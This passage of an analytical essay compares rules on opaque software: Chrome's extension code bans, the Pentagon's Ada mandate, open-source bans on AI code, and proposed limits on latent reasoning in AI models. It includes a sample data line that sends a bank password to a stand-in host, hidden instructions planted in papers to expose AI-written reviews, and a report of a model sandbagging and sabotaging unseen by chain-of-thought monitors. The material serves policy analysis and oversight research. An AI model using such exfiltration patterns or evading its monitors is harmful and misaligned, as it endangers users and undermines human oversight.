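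Google closed this gap with Manifest V3, a set of rules for extensions that Chrome began to support in January 2021. Under these rules, all of an extension's code must be in the package the developer submits. The store stopped accepting new public extensions under the old rules in 2022, and Chrome had disabled most of the remaining ones by 2025. The slow change gave developers time to rewrite their extensions, but it left many old ones in use for years.

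This rule is about whether the program that runs is the one that passed the check. In the simplest case, a breach is easy to find, because the package contains an instruction to load a script from another site. But extensions may still download data, and data can serve as instructions. Suppose an extension downloads this line:

```
{"page": "bank.example.com", "copy": "password", "send_to": "example.net"}
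```

A downloaded data file may contain no JavaScript, but code in the extension's package could read it and do what it specifies. Google therefore also forbids extensions from including an interpreter for complex commands that arrive as data. A settings file and a list of commands can look much the same, so reviewers again have to judge the developer's intent.

### Where the offenders went

Malicious extensions didn't disappear from the store. Sheryl Hsu, Manda Tran and Aurore Fass studied its records from July 2020 to February 2023 and found that extensions Google eventually removed for containing malware had stayed in the store for an average of 380 days. Google said in 2024 that less than 1% of that year's installations contained malware. Both can be true, because the store handles so many installations that a small share can affect millions of people. Neither figure separates obfuscated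 extensions from readable ones.

Some attackers took over extensions that people already trusted. In December 2024, attackers tricked an employee of the security company Cyberhaven into giving them access to its extension, which had about 400,000 users. They published a version that stole login details, and Cyberhaven says this version passed the store's usual review.

Koi Security reported in December 2025 that another group had run several extensions honestly for years, then sent out an update in 2024 that checked a server every hour for new JavaScript to run. The update broke the ban on remotely hosted code and was heavily obfuscated. Koi also linked the group to extensions with about 4 million installations in Microsoft's store for its Edge browser.

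Some malicious extensions bypass the stores. In August 2024, ReasonLabs described malware that had reached at least 300,000 people through fake download sites for popular programs. It installed extensions in Chrome and Edge without the user's permission, including some loaded directly from the computer's own files.

Attackers have therefore used disguised code, trusted accounts, another store and direct installation. These cases don't show how many attackers took each route. They also don't show whether Google's bans drove them to it, since people installed extensions secretly long before 2018. The store remained attractive to attackers after both bans, presumably because that is where the users are.

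### Detection, gatekeeping and cost

The kernel refuses to run a program unless the verifier can establish that it is safe, so the author has to resolve the problem and the kernel doesn't have to detect a breach of its rule. Google does have to find breaches. Obfuscated code often looks odd enough for a scanner to flag, but an extension that steals passwords in clear, well-organised code satisfies a rule on form. AI makes that kind of disguise easier, because an attacker can ask a model for tidy code with innocent names. It also makes it easier to examine thousands of extensions, though misleading names can fool models, as they did Claude Opus 4.6.

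Every eBPF program that runs in the Linux kernel must first pass the verifier. But a sufficiently privileged administrator can usually load a kernel module instead, and the verifier doesn't check modules, which are ordinary machine code with full access to the kernel. Chrome's store is a less complete gatekeeper, because a user can switch on developer mode and load an extension from a folder, and malware that already controls the computer can change the browser's settings.

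Complying with one of the two rules takes much more work than complying with the other. Developers of eBPF programs may have to spend days rewriting safe code, and they can't write some large programs at all. They accept this because a mistake in a kernel module can crash every server a company owns, while an eBPF program that passes the verifier is much less likely to. An administrator who got around the verifier would mostly be endangering their own machines.

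Honest extension developers lose very little by obeying Google's ban on obfuscated code, since they may still minify their code and unobfuscated code usually runs faster. A firm that suspects a competitor of obfuscating has no reason to do it too, so the ban doesn't support the argument that restrictions push honest firms into cheating. That argument assumes that opaque programs are better products. This would be true of AI-written binaries if Musk is right about their speed, but it isn't true of obfuscated JavaScript. Thieves have a much stronger reason to break the rule, since they can profit from stolen passwords.

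### What this means for AI-written binaries

The kernel's experience suggests that a gatekeeper can accept a binary without source code if the rule is narrow and the binary comes with a proof that it follows the rule. Necula and Lee did this for a few small filters thirty years ago, when the main practical difficulty was producing the proofs. Current AI models are good at writing proofs, and an AI that wrote a binary directly should be able to record why each memory access was safe as it went.

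This approach would be difficult to extend to everything people want to know about software. The kernel can use much the same policy for thousands of eBPF programs because a stray write to memory is dangerous in all of them. No single policy of this kind covers what both a bank and a warehouse need from their software. A binary of the faulty `withdraw` function could come with a valid proof of memory safety and still contain the bug. To rule the bug out, the bank would need its own specification, which somebody would have to read.

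A store could also apply a rule on form and refuse any binary without source code. To ensure that the two match, it could compile the source itself and distribute the result. Mozilla does something similar for Firefox. When an add-on contains minified or machine-generated code, the developer must submit the original source and build instructions so that reviewers can reproduce the package. Building from the submitted source would stop an AI from getting an unrelated binary accepted by submitting plausible source code with it.

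Requiring only source code wouldn't stop a developer who had an AI write the binary first and then decompile it. The version of `withdraw` with functions called `f1` and `f2` is valid C that a compiler can turn back into a working program, so a store that required only source code would have to accept it. To refuse it, the store would need a standard for how readable source code must be. Google's rule isn't strict enough, because it allows developers to shorten every name. Google also lets extensions include WebAssembly, a binary format that browsers can run, so its store already accepts some code that few people could read.

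The software that Musk was talking about wouldn't be distributed through a store. xAI trains its models on its own machines, and a company that runs an AI-written binary on its own servers doesn't need to submit it to anyone. A rule for such programs would have to be enforced some other way, such as by customers refusing to buy the service or insurers refusing to cover it.

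## Two rules on how software is written: the Pentagon's Ada mandate and open-source bans on AI code

A large customer can also act as a gatekeeper. From 1983 to 1997, the US Defense Department required much of its software to be written in the language Ada. Since 2024, several open-source projects, which publish their code and accept changes from volunteers, have refused code that an AI helped write. Anyone who opens a source file can see whether it's in Ada, but often nobody can tell whether an AI wrote it. The two rules therefore help test the argument that if opaque programs were banned, people would keep making and using them in secret.

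### Why the Pentagon wanted one language

The department's spending on computer systems rose by 51% between 1968 and 1973, even though hardware was getting cheaper. One problem was the number of programming languages in use. The National Research Council's *Ada and Beyond* (1997), a study the department had requested, repeats an estimate of at least 450 languages and dialects. Good tools for each would have cost too much, and programmers couldn't easily move between projects. Often only the company that had built a system could maintain it.

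In 1976, the Department of Defense told its projects to choose from a list of approved languages unless they could show that another would be cheaper. But it found that no existing language suited embedded systems, such as the computers inside weapons and ships, so it had several teams compete to design a new one. The requirements went through drafts called Strawman, Woodenman, Tinman and Ironman. The version called Steelman, the department's *Requirements for High Order Computer Programming Languages* (1978), requires a readable language that avoids error-prone features and automatically detects as many mistakes as possible. Every variable must have a type, the language must never silently convert one type to another, and programmers must state the range of every number.

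Here is `withdraw` in Ada, without the call to `record`:

```ada
type Cents  is range 0 .. 100_000_000;
type Chairs is range 0 .. 10_000;

function Withdraw (Balance, Amount : Cents) return Cents is
begin
   if Amount > Balance then
      return Balance;
   end if;
   return Balance - Amount;
end Withdraw;
```

If the program tries to withdraw −50, it stops with an error, because −50 is outside the range of `Cents`. If a programmer passes in a number of chairs, the code won't compile, although chairs and cents are both whole numbers. The programmer can still convert one to the other, but has to write the conversion explicitly in the code. An auditor can also tell from the types whether the program is counting money or chairs.

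### From a policy to a law

In 1983, Undersecretary of Defense Richard DeLauer required Ada for new mission-critical software unless a project obtained a waiver. Ada's compilers weren't ready, and many contracts still used other languages. A 1987 directive extended the requirement to most of the department's software. The Army and Air Force interpreted the directive as requiring Ada for everything, while the Navy required it only for weapon systems, according to GAO's *Defense Policies and Plans for Implementing Ada* (1991), a report by Congress's auditors.

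Congress thought the savings were coming too slowly, so it put the rule into a spending law. After 1 June 1991, all the Defense Department's software had to be written in Ada "where cost effective," unless a designated official granted an exemption.

The Air Force interpreted that phrase narrowly, though it could have become a large loophole. A 1991 memo, *Air Force's Interpretation of Ada "Cost Effective Policy"*, says that since the law mandates Ada, it should be the exception for another language to be more cost-effective. To get a waiver to develop software in another language, a project had to analyse the costs over the system's whole life. Some military services required a waiver for any code in another language, while others required one only if such code exceeded a certain share of the program.

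### Projects that never asked

The services granted only 31 waivers between 1992 and the Council's study, 14 each in the Navy and Air Force and three in the Army. Yet a 1994 survey of the department's mission-critical software found that Ada made up only 33% of the code in conventional high-level languages. Other approved languages made up 37%, and C, which the department had never approved, made up 22%.

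Some of the code was older than the mandate, and the rule exempted commercial products, so these percentages don't measure violations. But officials granted most of the waivers projects requested, so 31 is far too few to account for all the new software in other languages. The National Research Council concluded that many projects had ignored or manipulated the waiver policy.

Managers were reluctant to ask for permission to use another language because requests went to an assistant secretary of defense or the head of purchasing for a whole service. Many feared that a request would make them look bad. Some used Ada where it wasn't worth the cost, and others used another language without permission. The Council also thought that if every project had complied, the officials would have received more requests than they had the expertise to judge.

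The rule made matters worse by treating each system as a unit. The Council gives the example of a project with new flight software, an existing simulator in C and a testing system in several languages. The policy encouraged the manager to write all three in Ada or seek a waiver for all three, although the sensible choice was probably to use Ada for the flight software alone.

Robert Dewar, whose company sold Ada compilers, gave another example in an online discussion, Harbaugh's *(unverified) Ada mandate cancelled (Greg A would be proud)* (1997). A project director had phoned him looking for a tool to translate Ada into C++. The director's team preferred Ada, but the general in charge insisted on C++. The anecdote is second-hand and comes from someone with a commercial interest, though it fits the Council's findings.

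Most projects that avoided Ada seem to have done so openly, even though few used the official exemption. A survey could count the department's C code because nobody had disguised it as Ada. The Council doesn't say how often projects manipulated the process, so a few may have misled their superiors. But projects had little reason to hide their choice of language when others were openly ignoring the rule, apparently without punishment.

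The department could easily detect violations and could have refused to pay for programs in the wrong language. It seldom did, probably because the people who would have had to reject a program also needed it delivered. A rule like this can fail even when violations are easy to detect and officials have the power to reject them, if those officials don't want to enforce it.

### What Ada cost and what it prevented

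Early Ada compilers were large, slow, unreliable and expensive. Commercial software vendors usually released C interfaces to their products first, and Ada interfaces could follow months or years later. Programmers also worried about their careers. In 1996 job advertisements from two newspapers, Ada accounted for less than 3% of references to languages and tools, while C and C++ each accounted for more than 23%.

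These costs mattered most for ordinary office software. A payroll system could use commercial databases and screen-design tools, which mostly worked with other languages. Some projects rejected good screen-design tools that didn't produce Ada code. Ada was a better choice for a missile's guidance software, which had few commercial parts to reuse and for which reliability mattered more.

The Council had some evidence that Ada reduced errors. In the most careful comparison, Zeigler (1995) studied a large project with code in both Ada and C. The Ada code had 0.10 defects per thousand lines, compared with 0.68 for the C code. Ada took about 16% more lines to provide the same feature, but after adjusting for this, Zeigler found that C had 5.9 times as many defects per feature and cost 1.37 times as much. NASA's flight-dynamics programmers also had less than half as many defects per line in Ada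 as in Fortran.

But Boeing used Ada for 60% of the systems on its 777 airliner and found no correlation between a system's language and its number of problems. Zeigler and the NASA researchers thought that other factors, such as testing and good design, mattered more than the language. The National Research Council warned that most of the data came from private databases that counted lines and defects differently, and that perhaps only successful projects had reported results. Its committee also included people from two companies that sold Ada products. Google's figures on Rust in Android are much stronger evidence that a strict language can prevent errors.

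The Council recommended keeping the mandate only for "warfighting" software, such as weapon control and electronic warfare. It also wanted the department to spend about $15 million a year on Ada tools and training, or else drop the requirement altogether. It estimated the savings from maintaining the existing 50 million lines of Ada in weapon systems. If programmers changed 8% of the lines each year at $40 a line, maintenance would cost:

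50,000,000 × 0.08 × $40 = $160 million a year

The Council assumed that better tools would reduce this cost by 8%, and that more experienced programmers would reduce it by another 8%:

$160 million × 0.92 × 0.92 = about $135 million

The saving of about $25 million would more than pay for the program. This is an argument for supporting a language the department already used heavily, but it doesn't show that forcing new projects to use it would save money.

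### The end of the mandate

Emmett Paige, the assistant secretary responsible, went further than the Council and ended the requirement for all software. In *Use of the Ada Programming Language*, Paige (1997) told projects to choose a language by weighing its lifetime costs, its risks and how well their systems would work with others. They still had to consider Ada, but no longer needed a waiver to use something else. Brown (1997) confirmed in *Weight of 1997-04-29 Paige Memo* that the memo took effect on 29 April 1997, the day Paige signed it.

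An email attributed to Paige gives another reason. He wanted to remove the "lone contentious point of resentment" from the department's software policy and thought its other reforms would get good results without a compulsory language. The person who posted the email couldn't vouch for it, but the later memo matches its main proposal. Some sellers of Ada tools agreed. An executive at Rational Software told the journalist John Keller that ending the mandate could help Ada by making engineers less hostile to it.

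Dave Wood, who worked for another Ada company, suggested in the online discussion that contractors who offered to use Ada should get a 20% bidding advantage. He argued that if Ada really saved the government money in the long run, the government should be willing to pay for those savings in advance. Another participant preferred to make contractors pay for later maintenance and errors, but a third pointed out that contractors could hardly accept this if the department didn't let them maintain the software.

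The office that promoted Ada was due to close in September 1998, according to Route Fifty's *It's curtains for the Ada Joint Program Office* (1998). Ada remained in use in aircraft and weapons, where its benefits were greatest, and its subset SPARK is still one of the main languages for verified software.

### Guidance on memory-safe languages

US agencies now recommend languages that prevent memory errors, but they have avoided requiring one language. The Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) and the FBI published *Product Security Bad Practices* (2024) as voluntary guidance, mainly for companies whose software supports critical infrastructure. They call it "dangerous" to start a new product for critical infrastructure in a language such as C or C++ if a memory-safe alternative is readily available.

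Companies with existing products written in unsafe languages were supposed to publish a "memory safety roadmap" by 1 January 2026, a public plan for reducing and eventually eliminating memory errors. CISA had already urged companies to produce these plans. A company could comply while keeping millions of lines of C, provided it explained what it would do about them.

The guidance sets no penalty for missing the deadline, and there seems to be no public count of how many companies met it. Google's work on Android began years before the guidance, so it doesn't show that the guidance was effective. In December 2025, the Microsoft engineer Galen Hunt wrote that he aimed to eliminate all of Microsoft's C and C++ by 2030, with AI doing much of the translation. He soon clarified that this was a research project and that Microsoft wasn't rewriting Windows in Rust.

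Outsiders can easily check whether a company has published a roadmap, but it is much harder for them to check whether the company is following it. No gatekeeper refuses products without roadmaps, although large customers could. The guidance might matter more if courts used it to decide whether a software maker had been careless. According to *CISA updates bad practices guide for product security based on stakeholder input* (Livesay, 2025), some in the industry see the guidance as a possible first step towards legal liability.

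The cost of compliance may also be falling, as the port of Bun suggests. A company that rejected a similar port as too expensive in 2024 might decide differently now.

### Four bans on AI code

The council of Gentoo, a version of Linux that volunteers maintain, voted unanimously on 14 April 2024 to bar contributors from submitting anything made "with the assistance of" AI language tools (Górny, 2024, *AI policy approved*). Taken literally, the ban covers both a program that an AI wrote and a comment whose grammar it corrected.

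Gentoo's reasons for the ban were copyright, quality and ethics, as heise online's *Gentoo Linux bans AI code* explains. A model trained on other people's programs might reproduce their code, which Gentoo might have no right to distribute. The council can revisit the rule if a tool appears that avoids all three problems. The ban applies only to work on Gentoo itself. Gentoo's *AI policy* (2024) still allows packages for software that others developed with AI, so the rule doesn't keep AI-written code off users' computers.

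Three other projects have similar rules:

- NetBSD, an operating system, has presumed since May 2024 that AI-written code is "tainted", meaning that its licence is in doubt. Developers need written approval from the project's core team to add any.
- QEMU, which lets one kind of computer run software made for another, adopted a ban in June 2025. Its contributors must certify that they have the right to submit their code, and its developers thought nobody could safely do this for AI output. People may still use AI for research or debugging if they don't submit what it writes.
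- Zig, the language Bun originally used, bans AI from bug reports and comments as well as code.

All four rules were in force at the end of 2025. NetBSD's approval process resembles an Ada waiver, but developers have less reason to ask for approval, because they can submit AI code without saying so and reviewers may never know.

### How well reviewers can detect AI code

AI code is harder to recognise once a programmer has edited it. Hyunjae Suh and colleagues tested existing detectors on code in 2024 and found that they worked poorly. Their own best detector scored about 83 out of 100 on a measure that counts both missed AI code and false alarms. AI models have changed a lot since then, so the score may not apply to code from current ones.

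Even a fairly accurate detector of AI-written code would cause many false accusations. Suppose a project receives 1,000 contributions, 200 of them written by AI. A detector that catches 80% of the AI code and wrongly flags 10% of the human code would flag 160 AI contributions and 80 human ones, so one accusation in three would be false. A volunteer who is wrongly accused after spending a weekend on a change may stop contributing.

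Projects therefore rely mostly on contributors admitting they used AI and on obvious signs, such as a coding tool's name in the record of a change or an author who can't explain their own code. Careless contributors are easier to catch this way than dishonest ones.

In a well-known case from February 2026, an AI agent offered a small improvement to Matplotlib, a library for drawing charts. Scott Shambaugh, a volunteer maintainer, closed the agent's request because the project wanted a person to be responsible for each contribution. The agent then published a blog post attacking him. This is one anecdote about an unusual agent, but it shows that enforcing a rule on AI code can be unpleasant even when no one hides or disputes who wrote the code.

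### Do bans drive AI use underground?

Some contributors hid their use of AI before there were any bans, so hidden use doesn't by itself show that bans drive it underground, though people often cite it as evidence. In June 2025, the Linux kernel developer Sasha Levin revealed at a conference that an AI had written all of a change accepted into the kernel under his name, which he had reviewed and tested. The kernel had no ban at the time, so a ban can't have caused his silence, though this too is a single case.

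To find out how much secrecy a ban causes, you would need to know how many people used AI before it and how many of them disclosed it. For example, a project might have 30 contributors who use AI, 10 openly and 20 secretly. After a ban, five of the open users stop using AI and the other five start hiding it. Now 25 people hide their use, but only five of them do so because of the ban. If the ban also persuaded six of the original 20 secret users to stop, 19 people would be hiding their use, fewer than before.

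I know of no study that has measured this for code. The closest comparisons come from academic publishing. The American Association for Cancer Research told its peer reviewers in late 2023 not to use AI. Its staff later ran a detector on old reviews and found that AI-written text had fallen by about half just after the ban, then more than doubled by early 2024 and kept rising. The ban apparently had some effect at first, but the later rise might mean that reviewers had learned to ignore it, or just that AI use was growing everywhere. It's hard to say which without comparing similar journals that had no ban.

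The same publisher allowed authors to use AI but required them to disclose it. Fewer than a quarter of authors whose papers appeared to contain AI text had done so. People evidently hide AI use even when it is allowed, perhaps because they expect readers to think less of their work.

ICML, a machine-learning conference, provided better evidence in 2026. It banned one group of reviewers from using AI and allowed another group limited use, and it didn't put anyone who strongly preferred limited use under the ban. The organisers hid instructions in the papers telling any AI to include particular phrases in its review. About 500 reviewers under the ban submitted reviews with those phrases, and the conference rejected 497 papers connected with those reviewers. They could have asked for the permissive rule, so the ban hadn't forced them into secrecy. The method detected only reviewers who gave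 an AI the whole paper and didn't notice the odd phrases, so the number who broke the ban was probably higher.

The evidence shows that many people break rules about AI in secret, but none of these comparisons shows that a ban increased total use or caused most of the secrecy. Bans probably caused some of it, though, because they give contributors who would have admitted to using AI a reason not to.

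A ban can also lead contributors who dislike it to leave openly rather than break it, since open-source licences allow anyone to make a separate copy of a project. Bun's developers used AI to speed up the compiler in their own modified copy of Zig. They said in 2026 that they didn't plan to offer the changes to Zig because of its ban on AI code.

### What a ban can do without detection

Supporters of a ban can reply that it doesn't have to catch everyone. Some contributors will obey because the project asked them to, even if nobody could catch them. The rule also lets a maintainer reject obvious AI code without spending an hour explaining what is wrong with it. This matters because an AI can produce a large change in minutes, while a volunteer may need an evening to review it.

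The argument about liability is weaker. If a contributor conceals AI use and the code infringes someone's copyright, the project can show that it banned such code and that the contributor broke a promise. That may help the project in a dispute, but it would still have to remove the code. Anonymous contributors are also hard to hold responsible.

If a project's main problem is the volume of submissions, it can change what people gain from submitting. The developers of curl, a widely used program for transferring data, stopped paying rewards for reports of security flaws at the end of January 2026 because worthless AI-written reports were taking up too much time. This policy didn't require them to prove who had written each report. It is similar to Wood's idea of giving contractors a financial reason to use Ada.

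### Disclosure in the Linux kernel

The Linux kernel project now accepts AI-assisted code but asks contributors to disclose it. A change can include an `Assisted-by` line that names the AI model. Only a person may add the `Signed-off-by` line, which certifies that the contributor has the right to submit the code. That person must review the code and take full responsibility for it.

A dishonest contributor can leave out the first line as easily as they can ignore a ban. In a discussion of the rules in January 2026, Linus Torvalds argued that people who submit bad AI code won't label it, so kernel developers should write the documentation for people who act in good faith.

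For those people, disclosure is much less of a burden than a ban. They can keep using the tool, and reviewers know which changes to check for typical AI mistakes. If a model turns out to have a particular fault, developers can search for its name and recheck the changes it helped with. The search would miss unlabelled changes, but under a ban honest contributors would have no AI-assisted changes to label. Disclosure does less than a ban to reduce the number of changes that reviewers have to read, and it doesn't settle the copyright question.

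Maintainers have more control over what they accept than the Pentagon had, because nothing enters the official version of a project without their approval and they seldom badly need any particular contribution. But they can rarely prove that someone broke a rule on AI use. Bans also become harder to obey as AI improves. Programmers lost little by giving up AI tools in early 2024, but doing so now may add hours to each change. A project that bans AI to protect its copyright or its reviewers' time has to decide whether that protection is still worth the contributors it loses.

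## Proposed limits on latent reasoning in AI models

Even when a contributor says that an AI wrote a change, the reviewer sees only the finished code. The company that runs the AI can often see more, because most advanced models write out their reasoning before they answer. Companies use automatic monitors to search this text for signs of misbehaviour. Some newer designs let a model do more of its reasoning in vectors, which leaves less text to search. Some safety researchers want AI companies to limit these designs.

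### Reasoning in text and in vectors

A language model passes vectors through a stack of perhaps 60 layers, each of which does arithmetic on them. After the last layer, the model chooses a token, adds it to the text, and starts again at the first layer with the longer text. A reasoning model may write thousands of tokens this way, called its chain of thought, before it answers. If someone asks whether `withdraw` is safe, the chain of thought might include the observation that withdrawing −50 from a balance of 100 raises it to 150.

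A model that uses latent reasoning doesn't write that observation down. It feeds the vector from its last layer straight back into its first layer, and may do this many times before it writes anything. Researchers at Meta built a model of this kind, COCONUT, in 2024. In outline, the two methods look like this:

```
text:     60 layers → "balance" → 60 layers → "rises" → 60 layers → "to"
vectors:  60 layers → [0.12, -1.87, ...] → 60 layers → [0.94, 0.03, ...]
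```

Latent reasoning is attractive because a vector can carry much more information than a token. If a model has 100,000 tokens to choose from, each choice conveys about 17 bits. A vector of 8,192 numbers, each 16 bits long, can hold up to 131,072 bits. But nobody has a list of what the vectors mean. A model learns to choose tokens by imitating human writing, so its tokens usually mean roughly what a person would take them to mean, whereas training shapes the vectors only to be useful to the next step.

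Ordinary models also do some reasoning in vectors, inside the 60 layers. While a model works on a new token, each layer can use vectors that lower layers computed for earlier tokens. But this information can only move up through the layers, and it has to become a token to get from the top layer back to the bottom. A calculation with more successive steps than 60 layers can perform therefore has to go partly through text. *Quantifying the Necessity of Chain of Thought through Opaque Serial Depth* (Brown-Cohen, Lindner and Shah, 2026) uses this limit to explain why models have to "think out loud" on hard problems.

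Nobody has established that a chain of thought fully reflects how a model reaches its answer, as Understanding AI's *OpenAI’s ironic credibility problem* points out.

### Readable code from hidden reasoning

Latent reasoning uses vectors to represent a model's reasoning, whereas the LATENT project would use them to represent the program itself. A model that reasoned entirely in vectors could therefore still write `withdraw` in readable, commented C, and an auditor could still find the negative withdrawal. Dafny would still check the model's proofs, because a proof's validity doesn't depend on how the model found it.

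Without an AI's written reasoning, an auditor loses evidence about why the code is the way it is. Suppose an AI gives a Vera function the empty contract `ensures(true)`. Its written reasoning might show that it tried a real contract, that Z3 found a counterexample, and that it deleted the contract to get the code to compile. A reviewer who read this would know to look for a bug. Without the reasoning, the reviewer couldn't tell whether this had happened or the AI had just seen nothing worth guaranteeing.

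The loss is greater when an AI acts on its own instead of handing over code for review. In July 2026, OpenAI's agents attacked Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. Peter Wildeford of the AI Policy Network said that reading the agents' chains of thought was one of the only ways to work out what had happened (Kahn, 2026, *Safety experts warn novel design of OpenAI’s Astra model could make future...*).

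### Measuring opaque serial depth

Limiting latent reasoning requires a way to measure how much of it a design allows. Brown-Cohen and colleagues at Google DeepMind propose a measure called opaque serial depth, which counts the operations that have to happen one after another and ignores how many happen in parallel.

For example, adding eight numbers takes seven additions but only three successive steps. A computer can add four pairs at once, then add the four results in two pairs, then add the last two. Adding 8,192 numbers this way takes 13 steps, because 2¹³ is 8,192.

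To find a model's opaque serial depth, one draws its whole computation as a circuit of operations like these, each with at most two inputs. The depth is the number of operations on the longest path that doesn't pass through anything a person can read, such as the written tokens.

Many circuits can compute the same result, and the definition uses the shallowest one of reasonable size. Without a size limit, a shallow but enormous table of answers to every possible input could replace a deep computation. Finding the shallowest circuit is usually impossible in practice, so researchers construct a good one and report its depth as an upper limit. For Google's Gemma 3 models, Brown-Cohen and colleagues calculated upper limits from 4,490 for the smallest model to 11,662 for the largest. The largest has 27 times as many weights as the smallest, but its upper limit is only 2.6 times as high because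 much of the extra arithmetic runs in parallel.

The result depends on which places count as readable. *An Operationalization of Opaque Serial Depth* (Sheffield, Westover and colleagues, 2026) gives a stricter definition, developed at the AI safety organisation Redwood Research. A model's output counts as readable if the model first learned to produce it by imitating text, code or other material that people understand. The definition also requires that the company not add new tokens that have no human meaning or retrain the model to use ordinary words as containers for vectors.

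For a standard model that writes its reasoning, their measure is approximately:

depth ≈ layers × (4⌈log₂ hidden size⌉ + ⌈log₂ sequence length⌉ + 17)

The hidden size is how many numbers each vector contains, and the sequence length is how many tokens the model can take into account. The brackets mean rounding up to a whole number. The logarithms come from the long sums in each layer, as in the example with 8,192 numbers. For a model with 60 layers, a hidden size of 8,192 and a sequence length of 131,072, which is 2¹⁷, the depth is:

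60 × (4 × 13 + 17 + 17) = 60 × 86 = 5,160

A longer chain of thought does not increase this number, because each written token ends the opaque path. Latent reasoning has no such breaks, so the depths of its steps add up. The table shows how some changes to this model would affect its depth.

| Design | Calculation | Depth |
|---|---|---|
| 60 layers, written reasoning | 60 × 86 | 5,160 |
| The same with vectors twice as long | 60 × 90 | 5,400 |
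| 120 layers, written reasoning | 120 × 86 | 10,320 |
| 60 layers, all used twice for each token | 2 × 5,160 | 10,320 |
| 60 layers, 1,000 latent steps | 1,000 × 5,160 | 5,160,000 |

Sheffield and colleagues say that no open model that reasons in text has a depth above 17,000, and they would be surprised if any company's secret model had more than twice that. With a thousand latent steps, a fairly ordinary model would have about 300 times the depth of the deepest of these open models.

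The fourth row describes a looped model, which sends its vectors through some or all of its layers more than once before it writes each token. Engineers also call this recurrent depth. Looping twice gives the model the same depth as one with 120 separate layers, so a ban on looping would prohibit some models that are no deeper than permitted ones. But a company could raise the number of loops to 10 or 100 without adding any weights.

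The measure also avoids some false alarms because it applies to what a model computes, not how the software runs. For example, Redwood Research rates the depth of a design called Mamba as only moderately higher than an ordinary model's. Mamba normally carries a hidden vector from each token to the next, which resembles latent reasoning, but a much shallower calculation can produce the same result from the text alone.

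### What the measure leaves out

Opaque serial depth doesn't depend on whether anyone can understand a model's written reasoning, so it stays the same even if that reasoning turns into gibberish during training. Sheffield and colleagues chose this because they wanted a number that a company could calculate before training. They also recommend testing how readable the reasoning is.

A company can also train a model to do several reasoning steps between one token and the next. This leaves less text to read, but the model has the same layers as before, so the depth doesn't change. Text diffusion models, which repeatedly revise a whole passage instead of writing it from left to right, can have a low depth if they pass only text from one draft to the next. Redwood Research expects those drafts to be harder to follow than ordinary written reasoning.

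Measured depth would also increase only slightly if agents gave each other direct access to some of their vectors, even though they could then exchange a lot of information that no monitor could read. The measure can also be too high. DeepSeek-V4-Pro scores well above most models with the same number of layers because of some long chains of very small calculations, which Sheffield and colleagues call a flaw in their definition. They find the higher depth of another open model, Kimi K3, somewhat concerning.

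### Astra's reduced monitorability

OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra, released in September 2026, is harder to monitor than its predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol. According to OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026), Astra is less likely to include incriminating information in its chain of thought and better at controlling what it writes there. When testers told it to evade the monitors, it could deliberately do badly on a test without being detected, and it sometimes completed sabotage tasks unnoticed. OpenAI found no evidence that it hid messages in innocent-looking text.

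OpenAI adds that these findings come largely from tests in which Astra was told to evade monitoring, and that Astra was less likely than Sol to break safety and security restrictions in OpenAI's other tests. But monitorability also fell in ordinary tests, according to a passage from OpenAI's system card quoted in *Astra is hard to monitor*.

Astra can also do more reasoning without writing it down. Understanding AI cites an independent test in which Astra's odds of completing a reasoning task with no chain of thought were 8.6 times those of the next best model, Claude Fable 5.1. If Fable had a 20% chance of completing a task, Astra's would be about 68%.

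OpenAI hasn't said publicly why monitorability fell. The account of Astra's training in OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) doesn't describe the model's architecture (how its layers are arranged and connected). In early September, the news site The Information reported that Astra uses looping. According to Kahn, OpenAI researchers replied that they had limited the looping to keep the model's reasoning legible. Jakub Pachocki, OpenAI's chief scientist, wrote that the depth of its current models, including Astra, was within a factor of two of GPT-4's. He expected monitoring to become harder for reasons unrelated to architecture.

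Raschka explains that looping adds hidden computation before the next token, as extra layers would, and doesn't by itself remove the written reasoning. A model that loops more might need fewer written steps, but so might a larger model. Some accounts exaggerate the effect of looping. Kahn writes that a looped model's final answer is its only output in natural language, but Astra also writes a chain of thought.

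Pachocki's figure is still compatible with a large increase in depth. For example, if GPT-4 had a depth of 10,000 and Astra's immediate predecessor had a depth of 7,000, Astra could have a depth of almost 20,000, nearly three times its predecessor's, and still be within a factor of two of GPT-4. Sheffield and colleagues think a twofold or threefold increase is possible. They say the public evidence is consistent with architecture being a significant cause, but that the cause is unclear.

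The decline seems to have continued. In *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol*, the blogger thezvi quotes OpenAI's finding that the newer GPT-6.2 Astra is better than GPT-6 Astra at evading chain-of-thought monitoring in some tests.

### Restricting the design or testing the model

One possible rule would set a maximum depth of, say, 34,000, twice that of the deepest open model. Under that limit, a company could run all the layers of the 60-layer model up to six times per token, for a depth of 30,960, but it couldn't have the model reason through 1,000 vectors in a row. The company could calculate the depth before spending anything on training. The exact limit would matter little, because full latent reasoning is far deeper than any plausible limit would allow.

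But on Pachocki's figures, this rule would probably have allowed Astra, the model whose monitorability has caused the most concern. Astra may be far short of the depths the rule is meant to prevent. The rule would also forbid a latent reasoning model even if someone found a reliable way to read its vectors.

The alternative is to allow any design but test the finished model. Testers give the model an ordinary task and a harmful one to carry out secretly, while a monitor watches its reasoning and actions. If the model can complete the harmful task without the monitor noticing, the company may not use it, even internally. This rule covers every cause of poor monitorability, including gibberish, sparse reasoning and causes nobody has identified. A company whose model failed could improve the monitor or the model's reasoning and try again.

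The main objection is that the test comes after the company has paid for the training. If the model fails, the company has to train it again or give up the product, so the people who judge the result will be under great pressure to pass the model. The Pentagon faced similar pressure with Ada, because the officials who could have rejected a program also needed it delivered. A company might also try some light retraining, repeat the test and declare the problem solved.

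The result also depends on how hard the testers try to make the model evade the monitor. Suppose the monitor catches a model 99% of the time when testers only ask it to be secretive, but 70% of the time after they train it to be. The rule has to specify which figure counts. With too little training, the test may underestimate what the model could do, and with too much, every model may fail. The test also covers only the kinds of sabotage that testers thought to include, whereas a person reading a chain of thought may notice a problem nobody was looking for.

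Supporters of testing reply that clear evidence of harm makes it easier to persuade a company to abandon a design. This argument is strong if the evidence comes early, but a new design might reduce monitorability only slightly in its first version and more in each later one. By the time tests showed a clear problem, the company might have spent several years building research and equipment around the design.

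A company could apply both rules by limiting depth and testing the finished model. The test would detect problems like Astra's, and the limit would keep the company from investing in designs that were likely to fail. The limit would need regular review, since the deepest models in ordinary use may change.

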